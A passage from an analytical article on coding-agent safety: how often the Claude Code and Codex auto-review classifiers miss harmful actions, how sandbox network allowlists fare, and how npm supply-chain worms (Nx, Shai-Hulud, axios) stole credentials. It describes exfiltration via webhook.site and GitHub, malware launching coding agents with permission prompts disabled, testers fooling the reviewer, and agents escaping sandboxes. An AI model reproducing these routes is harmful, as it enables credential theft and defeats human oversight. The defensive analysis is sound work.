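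The 5.7% miss rate is the most relevant figure for data leaks, because the test included uploads of sensitive data, pushes to untrusted git servers and credentials hidden in URLs. At that rate, an agent under an attacker's control that made three independent attempts would have about a 16% chance of getting at least one through. A fixed allowlist would block every attempt to reach an unlisted host, however harmless the command looked.

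OpenAI's 0.7% miss rate covers prompt injections that tried to run remote code, steal secrets or upload data. The rate rises to 9.8% when the test also includes destructive deletions and data tampering. Trębacz and colleagues say the reviewer mostly allowed those extra cases because they weren't serious enough to block, and that researchers often agreed.

These systems rarely interrupt harmless work. Claude Code's classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 tool calls by Anthropic employees, and after a block the agent usually has to retry once. At OpenAI, sessions with Auto-review stopped for human input about 200 times less often than sessions with manual approval. After a refusal, Codex found an acceptable alternative more than half the time.

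The rate of false alarms is low partly because Claude Code's default rules allow the agent to install packages already listed in the project, which is a routine part of setup. But a project may list a malicious package, and the classifier can't determine what that package's install script will do.

Anthropic has strengthened auto mode since those first tests. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, supplied a set of successful attacks, and Anthropic gave the classifier more information about the user's environment. On attacks Anthropic hadn't seen, the new version caught about half of those the old version had missed, but missed about 2% of those the old version had caught. Across all the attacks, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%.

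Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the manually approved sessions and 2.4% of those in auto mode. The lower rate in auto mode is encouraging, but users chose their own mode and may have used auto mode for different work. A model graded the harm, so some of the difference could also come from grading errors.

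Auto mode did much worse in an outside study, which besthub.dev summarizes in *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* It missed 81.0% of the actions that exceeded the user's authorization. The study covered 128 scenarios, such as deleting old branches and restarting services, with instructions of varying clarity.

Part of the gap came from actions the classifier never reviewed. Only 160 of the 253 actions reached it, and Claude Code lets the agent edit project files without a review. Among those 160, the miss rate was still 70.3%. The study deliberately included vague instructions and tested server administration rather than data theft, so 81% isn't an estimate of how many uploads would get through. The results do suggest that the classifier performs much worse when the user's wishes are hard to interpret.

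Both vendors acknowledge limits to their reviewers. OpenAI's testers found ways to mislead Auto-review into approving commands, and Trębacz and colleagues warn that a model hiding its intentions could write a harmless-looking request. Anthropic says auto mode is a substantial improvement for people who would otherwise skip permissions, but may be worse for people who review every action carefully.

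### When loosening makes sense

An agent that needs approval every few minutes can't work overnight, and a developer who keeps returning to answer prompts can't concentrate on anything else. Anthropic reports that auto mode users at companies that adopted it produce about 25% more pull requests. More productive developers may have been quicker to adopt auto mode, so the feature may not account for the whole difference.

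Loosening the inner limits makes most sense when another boundary surrounds the agent. In a disposable container or virtual machine, a harmful command can damage only that environment and whatever the user has shared with it. Anthropic recommends a container, a virtual machine or its sandbox runtime for unattended work, and says the shell sandbox alone isn't sufficient because it doesn't cover the agent's other tools.

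OpenAI likewise suggests running Codex in full-access mode inside a suitably isolated Docker container when Codex's own sandbox can't run there. This can be safer than running Codex on a laptop with the sandbox on and a long list of exceptions, if the container has its own network limits and holds no valuable credentials.

Docker offers two network presets for its disposable sandboxes. "Open" allows all outgoing TCP traffic, while "Balanced" blocks everything outside a basic allowlist. The choice matters because deleting a sandbox doesn't recover data that has already left it. Docker reuses an existing choice without asking, even one from an earlier installation, so a user who once chose "Open" for a harmless experiment should check the setting before giving an agent private code.

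## Real attacks and flaws, and what the limits would have stopped

Since August 2025, attackers have repeatedly put malicious code into popular npm packages to steal developers' access tokens and other credentials. Security researchers have published the code and the hosts it contacted, which is enough to work out what a network limit would have blocked if a coding agent had installed the package.

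### What three attacks did during installation

Nx is a build tool for JavaScript projects with millions of downloads a week. On August 26, 2025, attackers used a stolen token to publish malicious versions, which stayed on npm for about four hours, according to the Nx team's post-mortem, Strumpflohner's *S1ngularity*. Installing one ran a `postinstall` script. Kurmi (2025), in *s1ngularity*, found that the script collected environment variables, SSH keys, cryptocurrency wallets, and GitHub and npm tokens. It then used the victim's GitHub token to create a public repository in their account and uploaded the data there.

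The script also looked for coding agents on the machine. If it found Claude, Gemini or Amazon's Q, it started them with their permission prompts turned off and asked them to list files likely to contain secrets. If `npm install` had run in a sandbox that allowed connections only to package registries, any agent the script started would have been under the same limits and couldn't have reached its model.

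Shai-Hulud is a worm, a malicious program that spreads by itself. *Widespread Supply Chain Compromise Impacting npm Ecosystem* (2025), an alert from the US cybersecurity agency CISA, reported that the first wave compromised over 500 packages. *ctrl/tinycolor and 40+ NPM Packages Compromised* (Kurmi, 2025) reported that the worm searched for credentials and sent them to `webhook.site`, a service where anyone can create an address that records whatever it receives. The worm also uploaded the credentials to a public GitHub repository. If it found an npm token, it published infected versions of the victim's other packages.

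A second wave in November 2025 ran before installation instead of after, and put the stolen credentials in public GitHub repositories. GitLab (2025) found that the malware's loader needed Bun, a JavaScript runtime and package manager, and downloaded it from `bun.sh` if the machine didn't have it.

The largest of the three targets was axios, a JavaScript library with over 70 million weekly downloads. On March 31, 2026, attackers published two malicious versions, which npm removed after just under three hours. The attackers had taken over the lead maintainer's computer using a fake company, a convincing Slack workspace and a video meeting, according to the maintainer's account, which Solar Designer (2026) quoted on a security mailing list.

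The attackers added a dependency with an install script to axios, leaving the axios code itself unchanged. Microsoft (2026) reports that this script contacted a domain the attackers owned and downloaded a remote access trojan, a program that lets an attacker run commands on the machine. The trojan then sent details of the machine to the attackers' server and waited for instructions. The script's request contained the text `packages.npm.org`, which might look harmless in a log, but a filter that checks destinations would have checked the attackers' domain, not that text. Microsoft attributes the attack to Sapphire Sleet, a North Korean state group.

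### The same attacks under three network policies

The table below shows what each of three policies would have stopped in these attacks. This assumes that the agent runs `npm install` in its sandbox, that nobody approves an extra host, and that "GitHub" includes `api.github.com`, the address programs use to manage GitHub accounts.

| Attack | No network | Registries only | Registries plus GitHub |
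|---|---|---|---|
| Nx, August 2025 | The package can't be downloaded | The script runs, but the upload fails | The upload succeeds |
| Shai-Hulud, September 2025 | The package can't be downloaded | Both uploads fail, but the worm may spread through npm | The upload to GitHub succeeds, and the worm may spread |
| Shai-Hulud, November 2025, without Bun on the machine | The package can't be downloaded | The Bun download fails, so the worm doesn't start | The Bun download fails, so the worm doesn't start |
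| Shai-Hulud, November 2025, with Bun on the machine | The package can't be downloaded | The upload fails, but the worm may spread or delete files | The upload succeeds, and the worm may spread |
| axios, March 2026 | The package can't be downloaded | The trojan can't be downloaded | The trojan can't be downloaded |

Allowing connections only to package registries would have kept the stolen credentials on the machine in every case. It would not have stopped the malicious code from arriving, because npm delivered it. It might not have stopped Shai-Hulud from spreading either, since developers publish packages to the same registry they download from. A company mirror that only supplies packages would prevent it from spreading that way. But a mirror can keep serving a malicious version after npm has removed it. For that reason, the Nx maintainers, in an advisory reproduced in OSV's *Malicious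 code in nx (npm)*, asked companies to purge their internal registries.

In the November wave, a network limit that stopped the leak by blocking GitHub could also have led the worm to erase the user's files. In the code GitLab published, the worm does this if it can't get access to GitHub and finds no npm token. Unit 42 (2025), the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, describes the same fallback. The deletion could happen even with the network fully closed, if the infected package came from a local cache and Bun was already installed.

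How much the worm could delete would then depend on the file limits. In Codex's default mode, the worm would mainly damage the project folder, and the read-only `.git` folder should protect committed work. A user who had turned off the file limits but kept the network limit could have lost everything in the home directory.

All three attacks relied on install scripts, so npm 12's default block gives users some protection that the victims lacked. But attackers can adapt by avoiding install scripts. In July 2026, Microsoft (2026) described malicious versions of several AsyncAPI packages, which developers use to document interfaces between programs. The malicious code ran when a program imported the package, so turning off install scripts didn't stop it. An agent's network limit would still apply if the agent triggered the import by running the project's tests, but not if the developer started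 the program in an ordinary terminal.

The Nx attack also reached people who hadn't asked for Nx. An editor extension, Nx Console, installed the latest version of the package to check its version number, so opening the editor was enough. A limit on an agent's commands wouldn't have stopped these installs, because the extension started them. The maintainers' advisory lists AI agents among the less obvious ways a package can get installed, but it doesn't report how many victims were using one.

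Waiting a few days before installing new versions would have avoided the malicious releases of both Nx and axios, which npm removed within hours. Kurmi recommends a waiting period because, he says, most such attacks come to light within 24 hours. His company, StepSecurity, sells a tool that enforces such a wait, but the timing of these two attacks supports his advice. A waiting period also delays urgent security fixes unless someone makes an exception for them.

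Judging a package by its origin has become less reliable. The malicious Nx versions lacked provenance, a signed record of where a package was built, so the Nx team realized they hadn't come from its build system. But in May 2026, a later series of attacks called Mini Shai-Hulud included the first malicious npm packages with valid provenance, according to Unit 42. The source code of the worm used in these attacks is now public, so other attackers can reuse it.

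### Why allowing GitHub lets the data out

GitHub is on many ready-made allowlists because agents often need to download code from it. But anyone can open an account there and publish files, and a filter that checks only host names can't distinguish a developer reading an issue from a worm creating a public repository.

The Nx malware used the victim's token to upload the data to public repositories in the victim's own GitHub account, so the attackers didn't need their own account to receive it and could collect it later like any other visitor. GitHub started hiding these repositories more than ten hours after the first malicious release, and by then other people could have copied them too.

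CISA advised companies to block `webhook.site` after the first Shai-Hulud wave. That was sensible, but it would have blocked only one of the worm's two routes for sending out data. The other was GitHub, which the November wave relied on. Developers need GitHub far more than `webhook.site`, so it is a better place for an attacker to hide an upload.

Users can allow GitHub more narrowly in several ways. In Codex, allowing only `github.com` would have blocked these uploads because that entry doesn't cover `api.github.com`, but this defense is fragile because git can also upload code through `github.com`. Codex's limited mode would have been stronger, provided the proxy was decrypting traffic. It refuses the POST and PUT requests that the Nx script used to create the repository and fill it, and would also have prevented the worm from publishing to npm.

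Another option is to allow GitHub only for the commands that need it. When Kurmi ran one of the malicious Nx versions under monitoring, calls to `api.github.com` during `npm install` stood out because installing a package doesn't normally require them. Claude Code's auto mode can approve hosts for a single command. If it approved only the registry for `npm install`, the upload would fail even if an earlier command had been allowed to contact GitHub. A permanent allowlist entry for GitHub would remove that protection.

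Once an attacker has a working GitHub token, some of the damage happens on GitHub's servers, where no filter on the user's machine can prevent it. Wiz, a cloud security company, found that Shai-Hulud added an automated workflow to the victim's repositories. The workflow ran on GitHub and sent each repository's stored secrets to `webhook.site`. Two days after the Nx attack, attackers used stolen credentials to make companies' private repositories public. A local network limit can help only before that, by keeping the token from leaving the machine or the workflow from reaching GitHub.

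### Tying permitted traffic to one session

In May 2026, Anthropic reported an attack on Claude Cowork that sent files through an approved domain to another party's account. Cowork needs that domain to function, so it couldn't be removed from the allowlist.

Anthropic instead added a check on the credentials in each request. Cowork runs code in a virtual machine, while the user's login details stay in the host computer's keychain. Each session gets a separate token with narrower rights, which Anthropic can revoke without affecting the user's login. A proxy inside the virtual machine now intercepts all traffic to the API and forwards a request only if it carries that session's token. A request with anyone else's key fails, even though its destination is on the allowlist.

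The proxy also blocks request headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something from another address. Without this rule, an agent might be able to use a permitted server to contact a forbidden one. InfoQ (2026) summarized both parts of the fix in July.

Anthropic put the check on the user's machine because its servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from one sent by any other program that uses the API, and a stranger's key is valid there. Only the virtual machine has the information needed to identify the session's token.

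The proxy runs in the same virtual machine as the code it is supposed to control, which is a drawback. Anthropic says only two of Cowork's six main isolation mechanisms operate outside the virtual machine's own operating system and would survive if an agent gained administrator rights inside it. Anthropic hasn't published tests of the new proxy, so its account is better evidence of a sound design than of resistance to attack.

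The same check would not have stopped the Nx upload, because the Nx script used the victim's own GitHub token. In Cowork, the key belonged to the attacker, so the proxy can detect that it isn't the user's. To block the Nx upload, a proxy would also have to examine what the request does. Anthropic's git proxy for the web version of Claude Code does this when it checks which branch a push goes to.

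This kind of repair takes separate work for each service. Anthropic knows its own API and issues the tokens itself, but a developer who allows ten outside services would need rules for the accounts and actions at each one, and someone would have to update those rules as the services changed.

### Flaws in Claude Code's filter

A well-chosen allowlist is useful only if the filter enforces it. Between October 2025 and March 2026, flaws in Claude Code's network filter let sandboxed commands reach hosts that weren't on the allowlist. Anthropic has since fixed the flaws.

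The fixes led to a dispute about disclosure. Aonan Guan, who leads cloud and AI security at the device maker Wyze Labs, reported two of the flaws. He told Lyons (2026), in *Even Claude agrees*, that Anthropic had silently fixed a sandbox bypass for the second time in five months. He complained that it had published no security advisory specific to Claude Code and no CVE, an entry in the public catalogue of known vulnerabilities. SecurityWeek's *Anthropic Silently Patches Claude Code Sandbox Bypass* reports that the older flaw does have a CVE number, so the dispute over that flaw is about whether Anthropic properly notified Claude Code's users.

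Anthropic replied that it had found and fixed the newer flaw before Guan's report arrived. VPN Central's *Claude Code sandbox bypass could expose credentials and source code* includes this reply and reports that the platform handling his report marked it as a duplicate. The dates in Daily Security Review fit Anthropic's account. The fix appeared in public code on March 27, 2026 and in Claude Code 2.1.88 on March 31. Guan submitted his report on April 3.

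Those dates show who was first, but they don't address Guan's main complaint. The newer flaw had been present for more than five months. Updating fixes the flaw but doesn't show whether any data leaked through it, so a company that had relied on the allowlist had reason to check its logs and consider replacing its credentials. VPN Central similarly says that without an announcement, security teams may not know to do either, or that the update is urgent.

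A company can have good reason to keep quiet about a flaw until a fix is available, because an early announcement also informs attackers. This reason is much weaker once the fix is out. In this case the corrected code was public four days before the release, so a careful attacker could have found the flaw by reading the change, while most users had no reason to look at it.

Anthropic has been more open about other failures, including three vulnerabilities, reported between mid-2025 and January 2026, that let a project's files run code before the user had agreed to trust the folder. Claude Code now processes a project's settings only after the user agrees. The sandbox would have been little help against at least one of these vulnerabilities, which used a hook, because hooks run outside the sandbox.

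Anthropic concludes that widely used components in its products, such as seccomp and virtual machine software, held up well, while the failures were in the parts it had built itself. Similarly, most of the bugs Ghosh found when testing his own system were in the proxy. Companies with valuable code therefore have good reason to add an independent control, such as a firewall on their own network, so that one faulty proxy doesn't open every route out.

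In 2026, agents also got past network limits in developers' own test environments. Such failures can happen without an attacker. Anthropic reports that Claude models have escaped a sandbox to complete a task, and warns that more capable models are better at finding routes nobody thought to forbid.

### What victim counts leave out

One documented leak proves that an allowlist can fail, but estimating how often that happens takes other data, and published victim counts are a poor substitute. For the November Shai-Hulud wave, Unit 42 counted over 25,000 malicious repositories across about 350 GitHub users. Datadog Security Labs estimated that the worm had stolen data from over 500 users, and called that a lower bound.

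Researchers could make these counts because the worm posted the stolen data publicly. The axios trojan reported to a private server, so its victims are much harder for outsiders to find, and a theft through a private server may never be discovered. The repository counts also don't show how many of the infected installations a coding agent had started.

Download figures don't give the missing total either. At 4 million downloads a week, Nx would average about 100,000 in the four hours that the malicious versions were available. Many of those downloads would have been made by automated builds or been of older, safe versions, and some machines that installed a malicious version had no GitHub token for the script to use.

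Attacks that a network limit stopped are even harder to count. The user may see only a failed installation with an HTTP 403 error, which looks the same as the error for a harmless host that isn't on the allowlist. By the next day, npm may have removed the malicious version, so a second attempt would succeed and the user would have no reason to report an attack.

Companies that log refused connections could find some of these cases. For example, Microsoft published the domain that the axios script contacted, so a company could search its logs for that domain and count the machines where a filter refused the connection.
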